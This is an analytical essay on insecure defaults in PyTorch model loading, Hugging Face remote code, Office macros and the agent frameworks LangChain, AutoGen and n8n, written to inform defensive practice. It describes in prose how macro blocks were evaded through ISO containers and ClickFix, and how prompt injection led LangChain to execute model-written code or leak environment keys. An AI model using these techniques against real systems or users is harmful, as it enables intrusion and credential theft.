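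A programmer in this position sees an error message with two suggestions, both meant only for files from a source the programmer trusts. The first is to run the call again with `weights_only=False`, which "will likely succeed" but can run arbitrary code. The second is to add the missing name to the allowlist. This is much safer, but it may take several attempts because a file can contain more than one unlisted name. Setting `weights_only=False` takes one edit and always deals with this error.

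Library developers also had a reason to write `weights_only=False` before the default changed. PyTorch printed its warning only when a call omitted the setting, so any explicit value silenced it. In DeepSpeed, a library for training large models, *Add explicit parameters for torch.load (#6751)* quotes the warning and gives every call an explicit value. The one unticked item on its to-do list is to change the values to `True` "where necessary". A developer who writes `False` to silence the warning also opts out of the new default, perhaps unintentionally.

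Others reacted after something broke. The contributor vviitani-amd proposed adding `weights_only=False` to fairseq, a library for language and speech models, so that the code would keep working "in the same way as previously" with PyTorch 2.6. The developers of flair, the library behind the harmless model that Hugging Face's scanner flagged, committed a similar change because their models need classes that PyTorch doesn't allow by default.

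Flair users call flair's own loading function and never type `torch.load` or `weights_only`. Flair's developers chose the unsafe setting, and users, whose computers would run any malicious code, have no reason to know. Even someone reading flair's source might miss the danger, because `weights_only=False` sounds like a request for a more complete file, whereas Ruby's `unsafe_load` has the word "unsafe" in its name.

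PyTorch recommends TorchFix for finding calls that need attention. The tool flags calls that do not set `weights_only` explicitly, so a call that sets it to `False` passes.

PyTorch users can overrule the library by setting the environment variable `TORCH_FORCE_WEIGHTS_ONLY_LOAD=1` before starting a program. This forces every `torch.load` call to use the safe loader, including those that pass `weights_only=False`. The opposite variable affects only calls that do not set `weights_only`, so it cannot override a programmer who chose the safe loader. This asymmetry is sensible, but few people will set a variable to guard against a danger they have not heard of, and those who do will find that flair's models no longer load.

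Lightning AI took a different approach with Lightning, its library for managing training, by adding `weights_only` to the library's own functions and letting PyTorch supply the default. Users therefore get the safe loader unless they ask for the unsafe one. In August 2025, matsumotosan (2025) had weighed up ways for users to resume training from a checkpoint. One rejected option was to use the safe setting everywhere and tell users about an environment variable if loading failed.

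Relying on PyTorch's default protects only users with a recent version. Hugging Face's Transformers library also supports older versions, and in January 2026 its developers found that a call that loaded the saved state of a random-number generator was still unsafe with PyTorch 2.2 to 2.5. *Fix unsafe torch.load() in _load_rng_state allowing arbitrary code execution (#43140)* explains that the code appeared to use an allowlist, but the allowlist did nothing on those versions. The fix was to set `weights_only=True` explicitly.

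The warnings also reached people who could do nothing about them. A user of Whisper, OpenAI's speech-recognition program, asked in *About Whisper open source and "weights_only=False"* about a message that had appeared every time they installed it. The call that triggered the warning was in Whisper's code. Node.js hides some warnings about installed packages to avoid alarming users in this way, but then users have no reason to press the packages' developers for a fix.

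### PickleBall writes a list for each library

PyTorch uses the same default list for every model, so the list has to be short. PickleBall, the tool that Kellas and colleagues built, works out a separate list for each library from the library's source code. It does not use the model file to make these lists, so an attacker cannot influence them.

Suppose a library contains these two classes:

```
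class Model:
    weights: Tensor

class Tensor:
    def __reduce__(self):
        return (read_weights, (self.filename,))
```

PickleBall keeps a queue of classes to examine and two lists, one of names a file may import and one of functions it may call. Starting from the class that the user expects to load, it proceeds like this:

1. `Model` has no `__reduce__` method, so pickle will rebuild it as an ordinary object. PickleBall permits importing `Model`, then adds its subclasses and the types of its attributes to the queue. Here the only addition is `Tensor`.
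2. `Tensor` has a `__reduce__` method that returns `read_weights`. PickleBall permits files to import and call that function.
3. The argument to `read_weights` is a filename, which is plain text and needs no further class. The queue is empty, so PickleBall stops.

A file for this library may now import `Model` and `read_weights`, and may call only `read_weights`. If the file names `os.system`, PickleBall substitutes a dummy object that raises an error when anything tries to use it. PickleBall delays the error until then because some harmless models contain leftover training records that mention unlisted classes, and these models still work if nothing uses those classes.

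The researchers tested the tool on the 84 malicious models and 252 benign ones from 16 libraries.

| | Malicious models blocked | Benign models loaded |
|---|---|---|
| PickleBall | 84 of 84 | 201 of 252 (79.8%) |
| PyTorch's restricted loader, default list | 84 of 84 | 157 of 252 (62.3%) |

All of the improvement comes from four libraries, including flair. PyTorch's loader refused all 95 of their models, while PickleBall loaded 46. PickleBall failed most often on models from two image-recognition libraries, YOLOv5 and its successor, because their files use inconsistent names for the same class. For the other twelve libraries, PyTorch's default list was already sufficient, and PickleBall did slightly worse because two speech models opened a second pickle file when they ran.

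The 79.8% figure describes this collection, not Hugging Face as a whole, because the researchers chose libraries with their own model classes, and 76 of the 252 models came from one of those libraries.

The lists are also far longer than they need to be. For one library whose models import 4 names and call 2 functions, PickleBall permits 773 imports and 61 calls. Kellas and colleagues know of no attack that uses only permitted functions, but they do not rule one out.

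PickleBall's allowlists are easier to derive than allowlists for the Java applications that Sayar and colleagues examined, because a model's class describes most of what its file will contain. Even so, PickleBall's researchers had to edit the source code of five of the 16 libraries by hand before their analysis would work. Producing a list then took a median of 14 seconds, quick enough for a library's maintainers to do it with each release. If flair's maintainers shipped a list with the library, users could load flair's models without the unsafe setting.

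### Safetensors leaves no room for code

Hugging Face took a more direct approach in September 2022 with safetensors, a format that can hold tensors and a little descriptive text and nothing else. A file starts with the length of its header, followed by the header itself in JSON, which might contain this:

```
{"layer1.weight": {"dtype": "F32", "shape": [2, 2],
                   "data_offsets": [0, 16]}}
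```

The entry describes a two-by-two grid of numbers that occupies the first 16 bytes of the data after the header. The loader copies those bytes into a tensor with that name. The format has no instruction for importing a class or calling a function, so the loader needs no allowlist. As with JSON, the user's program has to supply the rest. It builds an empty model from its own code and then fills in the weights.

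Safetensors files also load faster, because a program can use the numbers directly from the disk and read only the ones it needs. Some developers care more about this than about security. In a discussion that Casey and colleagues analysed, one developer said that safetensors mattered more for its much faster loading than as a precaution.

Adoption of safetensors has depended heavily on a conversion tool that Hugging Face runs. Anyone can use it on a public repository, and it converts the PyTorch files and proposes adding the safetensors versions. Casey and colleagues looked at 1,032 repositories that were older than safetensors and had changed in 2024. Of the 418 updates that added safetensors files, 95.7% were accepted proposals from the tool.

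However, most proposals get no response. Across some 35,000 repositories, 83.5% of proposals were still open and developers had accepted 13.9%. Many may have come from strangers, so owners who did not reply had not necessarily considered the format and rejected it. The acceptance rate also rose from 12.7% in 2023 to 30.6% in 2024. Some owners who replied wanted proof that the conversion had not changed their model, and a few had received files that crashed or gave worse results.

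The conversion tool was itself vulnerable because it opened each pickle file with `torch.load` before converting it. In February 2024, researchers at the security company HiddenLayer showed how an attacker could use a malicious model to hijack the conversion service.

Converting a model to safetensors does not remove the old file. Casey and colleagues found that 98.7% of the repositories that adopted safetensors had kept their PyTorch files, so programs can still download them. Kellas and colleagues surveyed repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month ten times between January 2023 and March 2025. In the last survey, two and a half years after safetensors appeared, 44.9% of the repositories still contained pickle files. Repositories with both formats accounted for 1.7 billion downloads a month, and those with only pickle for more than 400 million.

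Newer models are switching to safetensors faster. Llama 4, Qwen-3 and DeepSeek-R1, three widely used language models, were all released in the format. But people who adapt such models often upload a pickle file with the new weights to record their training settings, and that file can carry code just as a pickled model can.

In April 2026 Hugging Face handed safetensors to the PyTorch Foundation, which also oversees PyTorch. Hugging Face's *Safetensors is Joining the PyTorch Foundation* (2026) describes safetensors as the default format for distributing models on the site and says that its maintainers are working with PyTorch's developers so that PyTorch itself may use it to save models. PyTorch 2.8 had already added some support for checkpoints that several machines save together. The announcement gives no date for the larger change, and until then `torch.save` still produces a pickle file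 by default.

### Code that comes with the weights

Safetensors works only if the user already has the code for the model. Transformers includes code for many common designs, but researchers keep inventing new ones, and they often put the necessary Python files in the same repository as the weights. Transformers will download and run these files if the user passes `trust_remote_code=True`:

```
pipeline("text-generation", model="deepseek-ai/DeepSeek-R1",
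         trust_remote_code=True)
```

*An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting* (Siddiq, Romel and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a call that loads DeepSeek-R1. The model's weights are in a format that cannot run code, but the call also runs Python code from the same repository. That code has all the permissions of the user's program.

`trust_remote_code` is a better unsafe opt-in than `weights_only=False` in one respect, because its name includes both "trust" and "code". The permission is still broad, since it covers every Python file that the model loads from the repository. If an attacker takes over the owner's account, the same line of code may run the attacker's version the next time it downloads the model. Users can prevent this by pinning an exact revision, but Siddiq and colleagues found developers who confused pinning with setting `trust_remote_code`.

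The researchers found custom code in 36,697 of Hugging Face's 2.1 million repositories, or 1.74%. Two smaller sites, OpenCSG and ModelScope, had another 9,358 such repositories. To avoid counting code that never runs, they traced which files a program could reach while loading a model. It could reach about 67,000 of the 128,000 Python files.

They then ran four scanning tools on those files. One, Semgrep, flagged 4.6% of the Hugging Face repositories, mostly for unsafe deserialization, which means some of the custom code itself opens pickle files. A flag marks a risky practice but does not prove that anyone could exploit it.

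The search for malware found little. YARA, a tool that looks for known malicious patterns, matched something in 7% of the Hugging Face repositories, but more than four-fifths of the matches were for a file format used in 3D graphics. Almost all the malicious models that researchers have found on the site use pickle instead. That may be partly because a pickle attack does not need the user to set a flag, though scanners have also concentrated on pickle files.

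Siddiq and colleagues also read about 600 discussions among developers. Many developers thought the flag only let the library read a model's descriptive data, and did not realise that it ran code. Others understood the danger and avoided it, for example by copying the repository and editing its files by hand. Some public model rankings forbid the flag. None of the five sites in the study isolates the code in a full sandbox while a model loads.

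Developers often ask for a new model's code to be added to the official library, so that nobody needs the flag. The library's maintainers would then have to review and support each design. People created 4,898 repositories with custom code on Hugging Face in April 2025, the peak month.

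## Office macros: from a warning people clicked through to a block

A macro is a small program stored inside an Office document. People write macros to automate repetitive work, such as formatting a monthly report, and send them to colleagues along with the document. The usual language is Visual Basic for Applications (VBA), which can also download files and start other programs. This macro is for Word:

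```
Sub AutoOpen()
    MsgBox "hello"
End Sub
```

Word runs a macro named `AutoOpen` when somebody opens the document. This one displays "hello", but an attacker would replace the middle line with code that downloads and starts a malicious program.

For many years Office dealt with this danger by asking users for permission before running macros. In 2022 Microsoft began blocking macros in files from the internet instead. Security companies counted attacks before and after the change, and their counts offer some evidence on how a consent prompt compares with a block.

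### A button that attackers taught people to press

In 1995, a virus called Concept copied itself from document to document using `AutoOpen` macros, which Word ran without prompting the user. Microsoft then added warnings. From 2010, Office opened documents with their macros switched off and showed a bar with an "Enable Content" button. Pressing it ran the macros and made the file a "trusted document", so Office did not show the bar for that file again.

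The bar told users that a document contained macros, but not what they would do. The attacker wrote the document, so it could give people a reason to press the button. Proofpoint's *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World*, a July 2022 report from an email security company, explains that attackers typically told people the content was important and that they had to enable macros to see it. Malwarebytes' *Microsoft takes macros out of the equation for five Office apps* describes Word files that installed the malicious program Emotet this way. People who worked with macros also had to press the button for harmless files, which presumably made it a habit, and approval prompts for AI agents carry the same risk.

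Administrators could already stop users from choosing to run macros. Microsoft's *New feature in Office 2016 can block macros and help prevent infection* recommended a setting that blocked macros in files from outside the organisation. But the setting was still off by default in early 2022, as Sophos pointed out, and Microsoft does not offer such policies in the edition of Office it sells to smaller businesses. Like Java's serialization filter, the setting protected only organisations whose administrators knew to turn it on.

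### Blocking by origin

When someone downloads a file or saves an email attachment, Windows attaches a hidden label known as the Mark of the Web. Its essential part looks like this:

```
[ZoneTransfer]
ZoneId=3
```

Zone 3 is the internet. Zone 1 is the organisation's own network, and zone 2 is for sites that the user or an administrator has chosen to trust. Microsoft's *Macros from the internet are blocked by default in Office* sets out what Office now does with a file marked as coming from the internet:

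1. If the file is in a folder that the user or an administrator has designated as a Trusted Location, the macros run.
2. If the macros carry the digital signature of a publisher the computer already trusts, they run.
3. If an administrator has set a policy on macros, Office follows it.
4. If the user pressed Enable Content for this file before the change, the macros run.
5. In all other cases, Office blocks the macros.

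Before 2022, the last step in running a downloaded file's macros was to click "Enable Content" in a warning bar. Now the user sees a "Security Risk" banner whose only button, "Learn More", opens a page about the danger. To run the macros anyway, the user has to find the file in Windows, open its Properties and tick a box marked "Unblock", which removes the mark showing that the file came from the internet. An attacker could write instructions for this too, but a victim is less likely to do it out of habit.

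Office decides whether to block a macro by using the file's origin as a proxy for trustworthiness, without examining what the macro does. As a result, it blocks some harmless macros and fails to block some harmful ones.

| File | What Office does by default |
|---|---|
| A spreadsheet attached to an email | Blocks the macros |
| A spreadsheet on the company's own server, opened through the server's numeric address | Blocks the macros, unless an administrator has listed the server as trusted |
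| A spreadsheet that OneDrive, Microsoft's file-sharing service, has synced to the computer | Shows the old bar with Enable Content, because the file has no mark |
| A download that the user has copied to a memory stick in the older FAT32 format | Shows the old bar, because FAT32 cannot store the mark |

The OneDrive case could help an attacker who has taken over a colleague's account and can add files to a shared folder. Microsoft warns of a similar risk when organisations mark their SharePoint sites as trusted, since anyone allowed to add files there can add macros. The block also applies only to Office on Windows.

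### Withdrawn and restored within three weeks

Microsoft announced the block on 7 February 2022 in *Helping users stay safe* (Kellie_msft, 2022). In a passage Thurrott quotes, it explained that Office had warned people about macros but "users could still decide to enable the macros by clicking a button". Users of preview versions began receiving the block on 12 April.

On 6 July the developer Vince Hardwick was making a video about the new banner for a company that makes a macro-based toolkit, but could not get the banner to appear. Hardwick asked on Microsoft's site whether Microsoft had reversed the change. No Longer Set's *Microsoft Backtracks (Temporarily?) on Policy to Block All Macros* quotes the reply from a Microsoft employee, who confirmed the rollback and apologised that it had started before any announcement.

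Microsoft attributed the withdrawal to "feedback" in its official notice, reproduced in BornCity's *Microsoft does not want to block macros in Office by default* (2022). The Record reports that some clients had complained, and that security experts then heavily criticised Microsoft for giving way. According to Sophos, Microsoft soon said the withdrawal was temporary, to allow for changes "to enhance usability". On 20 July it announced that it would resume the rollout, citing new instructions for users and administrators. General release began on 27 July, and the slower update schedules that many large organisations use followed between October and January.

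PyYAML's maintainers had also withdrawn a safe default soon after releasing it, but they never restored it. Microsoft publicly committed to the default it had withdrawn while it was still dealing with customers' complaints, and it gave those customers better instructions instead of weakening the protection.

### What Proofpoint counted

Proofpoint reported in 2022 that attackers' use of macros in email attachments fell by about 66% between October 2021 and June 2022. The company counted campaigns that its researchers had analysed by hand, not individual messages. The figure covers both VBA and XL4, an older macro language found only in Excel. Microsoft had said in October 2021 that it would also switch off XL4 by default.

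The underlying numbers come from press reports on Proofpoint's research:

| Period | Campaigns that used macros |
|---|---|
| All of 2021 | More than 700 with VBA and almost as many with XL4 |
| October 2021 | Just under 70 with VBA |
| June 2022 | About 21 with VBA |
| January to March 2023 | Hardly any of either kind |

Vumetric's *No more macros?* (2023) gives the figures for 2021, and Computer Weekly gives those for the two individual months. CyberScoop's *Cybercriminals have adapted since Microsoft's decision to block macros* quotes Proofpoint as saying that macros had "barely made an appearance" in 2023.

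Comparing June 2022 with October 2021 overstates the decline a little, because October was somewhat busier than the average of about 58 campaigns a month (700 a year). The number of VBA campaigns in June 2022 was still more than 60% below that average.

The timing of the fall is harder to explain. By the end of June, Microsoft had not yet begun the lasting general release of the VBA block, and users on slower update schedules were months away from receiving it. Most users had therefore not yet met the extra barriers that Computer Weekly credited for the fall. Proofpoint argues that attackers changed their methods in advance, in response to the announcements. This is plausible, because a criminal group that depends on macros has good reason to test alternatives before a published deadline. But the monthly counts do not fall steadily after February. VBA campaigns rose a little in March and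 April, and XL4 campaigns jumped in March, probably because the group behind Emotet was sending more. If one group can change the total that much, some of the fall by June may have been chance.

The figures for early 2023 are better evidence that the block worked. By then it had reached all the main update schedules, and macros stayed rare for three months instead of dipping for one. There is still no comparison group of similar users who kept the old prompt. However, people had been able to refuse macros for more than a decade, and in 2021 attackers still ran more than 700 VBA campaigns that depended on someone clicking to enable them.

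### Where the attackers went

Many attackers first looked for ways around the mark. One was to put the spreadsheet inside an ISO file, a copy of a whole disc that Windows can open like a folder. It worked like this:

1. The victim downloads the ISO file, and Windows marks it as coming from the internet.
2. The victim opens it and sees a spreadsheet. Windows has marked the container but not the spreadsheet inside.
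3. Office finds no mark on the spreadsheet and shows the old bar with Enable Content.

Attackers who did this went to some trouble to get the prompt back, which suggests that they did not consider it much of an obstacle. Others stopped using macros and put a malicious program in the container, or sent Windows shortcuts (LNK files), which can run a command when someone double-clicks them.

Proofpoint found that campaigns using containers or shortcuts rose by nearly 175% between October 2021 and June 2022. The number using shortcuts rose by 1,675%, although an increase that large usually means there were very few to begin with. At least ten of the groups Proofpoint tracked had started using shortcuts since February 2022, which is better evidence of a real shift.

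None of the replacements lasted as long as macros had. In November 2022 Microsoft fixed part of the weakness that had made ISO files attractive to attackers, and the main criminal groups used them much less afterwards. Use of shortcut files had already peaked by September. Attackers also hid malicious files inside web pages attached to emails, and from December they tried documents for OneNote, Microsoft's note-taking program. CISO2CISO reports more than 120 OneNote campaigns within a few months. A group that Proofpoint calls TA570 had relied almost entirely on macros, but later used as many as six methods in one month.

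Other companies saw a similar shift, though its size varied. IBM observed that by 2023 attackers were using fewer macros, disk images and files hidden in web pages, and more links and PDF files. HP's security division counted 588% more attacks through Excel add-ins in the last quarter of 2021 than in the quarter before, according to the Journal of Accountancy. That surge came before Microsoft announced the VBA block, and Proofpoint found only a slight increase in add-ins.

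By 2025 one prominent group, TA584, was using ClickFix, as SANS notes. In this technique, attackers use a fake error message or security check to persuade the victim to copy a command and run it. Like the old trick of getting users to click Enable Content, it relies on the victim's cooperation, but it doesn't need Office, so blocking macros doesn't stop it.

### Fewer macros, but how much less harm?

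Proofpoint's figures show that attackers largely gave up macros, but they don't measure how many computers attackers infected, how much money victims lost, or how often the replacements succeeded. Each campaign counts once, whether it consists of a handful of messages or several million. Attackers had used macros for years and could have switched to shortcuts or disk images at any time, so the replacements were probably less effective or more work. If so, the block reduced harm, but by an unknown amount.

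The total number of attempts did not obviously fall. Trend Micro blocked about 4.3 million malicious files in email in 2022, 29% more than the year before, according to its *Email Threat Landscape Report*. But this figure comes from one company's product and would rise if more customers bought it or if its detection improved. It also counts files that the company stopped, which did no harm to those customers.

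Proofpoint, Trend Micro and HP all sell protection against these attacks, so they benefit if customers believe the danger is growing or changing quickly. That is a reason to be cautious about Proofpoint's claim that attackers' constant experimentation is a "new normal". It is a weaker reason to doubt the fall in macros, because that is good news about a free change made by another company. Microsoft could have checked the figures against its own records, but declined to comment on them when The Record asked.

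A better test would compare infections at organisations that received the block in July 2022 with those at similar organisations that received it in January 2023. Microsoft's staggered release created these two groups, but the companies' published counts do not separate them.

### VBScript's three phases

VBScript is a related scripting language that has been part of Windows for almost 30 years. Microsoft announced in 2023 that it would retire the language, and in May 2024 it published a three-phase plan (Visual Studio Magazine, 2024).

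| Phase | Date | Status of VBScript |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Since Windows 11 version 24H2 | An optional feature, switched on by default |
| 2 | Around 2027 | Switched off by default, but users can turn it back on |
| 3 | No date | Gone from new versions of Windows |

In September 2025, Microsoft's *Prepare your VBA projects for VBScript deprecation in Windows* (2025) dated the second phase to "approximately 2026 or 2027". The first phase was still in force on 17 October 2026, when Ebi Study, a Japanese training site, checked Microsoft's current documents for its guide *VBScript廃止はいつ？* (2026) and found the second phase due around 2027.

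Microsoft still has to replace some of its own scripts, including a VBScript tool that many businesses use to activate Windows. TechSpot's *Microsoft warns that killing VBScript could break Windows activation for businesses* (2026) reports that a replacement reached Windows 11 in a preview update in August 2026, and that Windows Server will not have one until its next major release.

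## Agent frameworks that run code written by a model

In late 2022 and 2023, developers began using agent frameworks to automatically run programs written by language models. These frameworks are libraries that connect a model to tools, data and other software. The model writes each program in answer to a question, and the program carries no mark of origin. A Word macro, by contrast, exists before anyone opens the document, so a scanner can examine it and Office can check where the file came from.

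These frameworks are often meant to run code, so their maintainers could seldom offer a replacement that did the same job without running a string as code, as PHP's developers did for the `/e` modifier. Three widely used projects, LangChain, AutoGen and n8n, have instead mostly changed where the code runs or required users to opt in.

### A calculator that ran Python

Early language models were bad at arithmetic but fairly good at writing short programs. LangChain, a Python framework first released in October 2022, took advantage of this in a component called `LLMMathChain`. In outline, it worked like this:

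```
question = "What is 12 times 34?"
program = ask_model("Write Python that answers: " + question)
exec(program)
```

The model might write `print(12 * 34)`, and `exec` would run this and print 408. But a question that contained instructions for the model could lead it to write something other than arithmetic, and `exec` would run that too. GitLab's *CVE-2023-29374*, dated 5 April 2023, lists every version up to 0.0.131 as vulnerable.

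Users on LangChain's issue tracker had suggested running the code in a sandbox. The maintainers instead replaced `exec` with numexpr, a library that evaluates mathematical expressions, so the model had to write an expression such as `12 * 34` rather than a whole program. This was sensible because a calculator needs only arithmetic. But numexpr's `evaluate` function could also run arbitrary code, according to GitLab's *CVE-2023-39631* (2023), and LangChain made the library an optional extra that autumn.

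A similar component, `PALChain`, also passed the model's Python to `exec`. Its maintainers kept `exec` and added a check to reject dangerous programs before running them. By October 2023 someone had bypassed the check with an import it did not prohibit, according to GitLab's *CVE-2023-44467* (2023). The next fix could also be bypassed through several of Python's internal names, including `__import__` and `__subclasses__` (OSV's *PYSEC-2026-375* (2026)). PyYAML's maintainers had gone through much the same sequence with `FullLoader` three years earlier.

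### Moving the danger to another package

In July 2023 LangChain's maintainers moved every component with a CVE from the main package to a new one, `langchain_experimental`. In its announcement, "Goodbye CVEs, Hello `langchain_experimental`" (LangChain, 2023), the company explained that the framework had begun as an experiment and it now wanted to separate the risky uses from those that businesses could rely on.

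LangChain's maintainers released the new package on 22 July and planned to remove the old components from the main one on 28 July. They promised at least a week's notice for later moves, whereas Microsoft had given BinaryFormatter's users four years. In the project's discussion, *LangChain Experimental, CVEs and Repo Restructure*, one developer asked how badly the move would affect an application that used the database and spreadsheet agents. Another reported that they could no longer import the database component from its old location and that the new location didn't work either.

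The maintainers told users to expect "zero changes to functionality" in the components they moved, so a program that switched to the new package was as exposed as before. The move helped people who installed only the main package, because they could no longer use one of these components without noticing. The new package's name also indicated that the code was experimental, but not that it might be dangerous.

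The move also made it easier to add risky code. LangChain said it had been slow to accept experimental features and hoped the separate package would help it accept them faster. On 5 October 2023, about ten weeks after the package appeared, it gained a component for symbolic mathematics. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-374* (2026) reports that the component passed text to a function that uses `eval`, which was essentially the original calculator's flaw.

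LangChain has since stopped maintaining the package. Ecosyste.ms, a catalogue of open-source projects, lists its repository as archived, with the last change on 22 May 2026. People who need the old behaviour can still download the package without support, as they can with Microsoft's BinaryFormatter package. LangChain warns on the download page that parts of the package may be dangerous outside a sandbox.

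### LangChain loads its own data

LangChain's next important change of default concerned deserialization. LangChain saves its objects as JSON and uses the key `lc` to mark values that it should turn back into an object:

```
{"lc": 1, "type": "constructor",
 "id": ["langchain_core", "messages", "ai", "AIMessage"],
 "kwargs": {"content": "hello"}}
```

The `load` function reads this and builds an `AIMessage`, a message from the model, with the text "hello". The `id` line names the class, as a YAML tag can. Ordinary data might also contain the key `lc`, so LangChain has to label such data when saving it to prevent it from being treated as an object later. LangChain did not add these labels until December 2025.

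A model's reply includes fields besides its text, and a prompt injection can influence their contents. LangChain often saved replies and loaded them later, for example to keep a conversation's history. When it loaded a reply, it could turn values planted by an attacker into objects. Cyata (2025), the security company whose researcher found the flaw, counts twelve vulnerable features. A developer could use one of them without calling `load`, much as Rails developers had accepted YAML without knowing it.

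LangChain already had an allowlist of classes, but it was broad. LangChain also let saved data include the values of environment variables, which are settings the operating system passes to a program and often hold passwords and access keys. Cyata found a class on the allowlist that makes a web request as soon as LangChain creates an object from it, and that request could send a key to an attacker's server. Cyata found no way to run arbitrary code through `load` alone. For that, the program would also have to use a loaded template written in Jinja2, a format for filling in text.

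Cyata reported the flaw, CVE-2025-68664, on 4 December 2025, and LangChain published its advisory within three weeks. As well as labelling the data properly, the maintainers changed three defaults in `load`, which OSV's *PYSEC-2026-373* (2026) describes:

| Until December 2025 | Now | To get the old behaviour |
|---|---|---|
| Builds any class on a broad allowlist | Builds only classes from LangChain's core package | Pass a longer list, or `"all"`, as `allowed_objects` |
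| Looks up environment variables on request | Ignores the request | `secrets_from_env=True` |
| Accepts Jinja2 templates | Refuses them | `init_validator=None` |

LangChain told most users they would not need to change anything, even if they loaded saved connections to OpenAI's or Anthropic's models. That seems to conflict with the first row, because the code for those connections is in separate packages.

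A second flaw appeared in May 2026. Some of LangChain's own older components set `allowed_objects="all"`, so the stricter default never applied to them, just as PyTorch's safe default did not protect users of libraries that set `weights_only=False`. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2564* (2026), the maintainers deprecated those components. They also plan to require every caller of `load` to specify which objects the function may build, a requirement similar to the one PyYAML adopted in 2021. LangChain's reference page for the function, *load*, now advises treating saved objects as "executable configuration rather than plain text".

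### AutoGen moves code into a container

AutoGen, which Microsoft released in September 2023, lets several agents work on a task by sending one another messages. In the usual arrangement, an assistant agent writes code and a second agent, the "user proxy", runs it and sends back the result. The assistant can then correct its mistakes and try again. A programmer might set up the second agent like this:

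```
user_proxy = UserProxyAgent("user_proxy",
    code_execution_config={"work_dir": "coding"})
```

At first, this agent ran the assistant's code directly on the programmer's computer, with the same access to files as AutoGen itself. The developers strongly recommended Docker, which runs software in a container, a kind of sandbox with its own files and processes, but programmers had to read the recommendation and act on it.

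Since version 0.2.8, released in January 2024, the same lines of code start a Docker container, run the program inside it and shut it down. Microsoft's *Code execution in docker* (2024) attributes the change to the fact that users, especially new ones, could easily overlook the risk. It does not mention a specific attack or vulnerability. The developers noticed the problem about four months after AutoGen's release, before many programs depended on the old default.

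If Docker is not running, AutoGen stops with an error. The user can start Docker, turn off code execution, or return to the old behaviour by adding `"use_docker": False` to the configuration. Setting the environment variable `AUTOGEN_USE_DOCKER` to `False` restores the old behaviour for every agent at once. Microsoft deliberately made opting out easy because it recognised that people trying out AutoGen might not care about the risk. It mainly wanted them to know that the code would run on their own machine.

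Nobody seems to have counted how many users installed Docker and how many turned it off. At least one user built an alternative. *AutoGen Code Interpreter with E2B* (Tizkova, 2024) describes this contributor's example, which sends the code to a sandbox in the cloud, though Tizkova works for the company that sells the sandbox. *Code execution*, from the AutoGen offshoot AG2, gives an example that runs the code on the user's own machine but requires a person to respond before each step. The example also puts the code's files in a temporary folder, which keeps them tidy but doesn't stop a program that starts there from opening files elsewhere on the computer.

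The AG2 example is reasonable for someone learning the library, but its safety depends on one setting, `human_input_mode="ALWAYS"`. A reader who copies the example and gets tired of answering prompts can change that setting without touching the part that runs code.

Code run in Docker can still do harm. E2B (2023), the cloud-sandbox company, quoted Docker's own warning that a container's default settings "may provide incomplete isolation". But a command that mistakenly deletes files does far less damage in a container than on the user's machine.

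### n8n waits for version 2.0

In n8n, people build automated workflows by connecting blocks called nodes. One node might read incoming email, and another might add a row to a spreadsheet. The Execute Command node runs system commands, and the Code node runs JavaScript or Python. People usually write this code themselves, but a workflow can pass text from a model into the code. AI agents in n8n can also use some nodes as tools.

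Snyk's *n8n@2.0.0 vulnerabilities* lists the Execute Command node itself as a flaw because anyone allowed to edit workflows could run commands on the server. In response, n8n's maintainers advised administrators to turn the node off if they did not need it. They did not change the code but said a future version might change the default.

That version was 2.0, which reached general release in December 2025. n8n said it had been collecting security improvements since version 1.0 in July 2023, but all of them had to wait because it had promised not to break existing workflows except in a new major version. The promise spared users frequent disruption, but it also left the less safe defaults in place for almost two and a half years. AutoGen's developers had made a similar change in a minor release.

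n8n's *v2.0 Breaking changes* lists the new defaults and how to reverse them:

| New default | To get the old behaviour |
|---|---|
| The Execute Command node is off | Remove it from the list in `NODES_EXCLUDE` |
| Code nodes cannot read environment variables | `N8N_BLOCK_ENV_ACCESS_IN_NODE=false` |
| Code nodes run in a separate process called a task runner, which blocks `eval`-style features | `N8N_RUNNERS_INSECURE_MODE=true` allows the blocked features |
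| File nodes can open files in only one folder | Give other folders in `N8N_RESTRICT_FILE_ACCESS_TO` |

n8n 2.0's use of a separate process partly reversed an earlier decision. In version 1.0, n8n had made all workflows run in its main process by default, because it thought separate processes started more slowly and offered only "marginal benefits" (n8n's *v1.0 migration guide*). That decision was about speed and simpler code. Versions before 2.0 also ran Python inside n8n, in a sandbox that anyone who could edit a workflow could escape to run commands on the server (OSV's *CVE-2025-68668*). Administrators could already switch to task runners before 2.0 made them the default.

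n8n prepared its users better than LangChain had in 2023. Administrators could run a report that listed the workflows that would break, in order of severity. They could also turn on several of the new settings before upgrading, and version 1 continued to receive security fixes for three months.

The change still confused some users. In *[v2.2.3] Cannot publish/activate workflow*, a user reports that workflows with the Execute Command node stopped working after the upgrade, with the message "Unrecognized node type". This sounds like a broken installation, and nothing in the message indicates that n8n turned the node off deliberately or that a setting would bring it back. In *Unable to re-enable Execute Command node in n8n 2.0*, a user had read about the change and added the node to a list of nodes to include, but it still did not appear. n8n's instructions were to edit the list of nodes to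 exclude.

Users soon shared n8n's advice for turning the node back on. In *Execute Command Node has removed*, one user posted it, including the example `NODES_EXCLUDE="[]"`. Another, who had used the node heavily, asked where to put the setting and then reported that it worked. The empty list turns on every node that n8n had disabled, including one that watches files on the server. n8n also suggests removing from the list only the nodes a user needs, but it gives no ready-to-copy example of this safer setting.

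The main changes in the three projects compare as follows:

| | Old default | New default | What prompted the change | How long it took |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LangChain's calculator (2023) | Runs the model's Python | Evaluates a mathematical expression | Users' reports and a CVE | About six months after LangChain's first release |
| AutoGen (January 2024) | Runs code on the user's machine | Runs it in a Docker container | The developers' worry about new users | About four months after release |
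| n8n's Execute Command node (December 2025) | On | Off | Security advice and a new major version | Almost two and a half years after 1.0 |
| LangChain's `load` (December 2025) | Reveals environment variables on request | Ignores the request | A researcher's report | About two and a half years, but under three weeks after the report |

### Does the word "dangerous" help?

LangChain has also tried putting a warning in the name of the setting. One of its components lets a program search a collection of documents and give the relevant passages to a model. It saves part of the search index with pickle. Since early 2024, LangChain has refused to load an index unless the programmer writes this:

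```
FAISS.load_local(folder, embeddings,
                 allow_dangerous_deserialization=True)
```

Similarly, a programmer has to set `allow_dangerous_code=True` before LangChain's agent for analysing tables will run the Python that a model writes.

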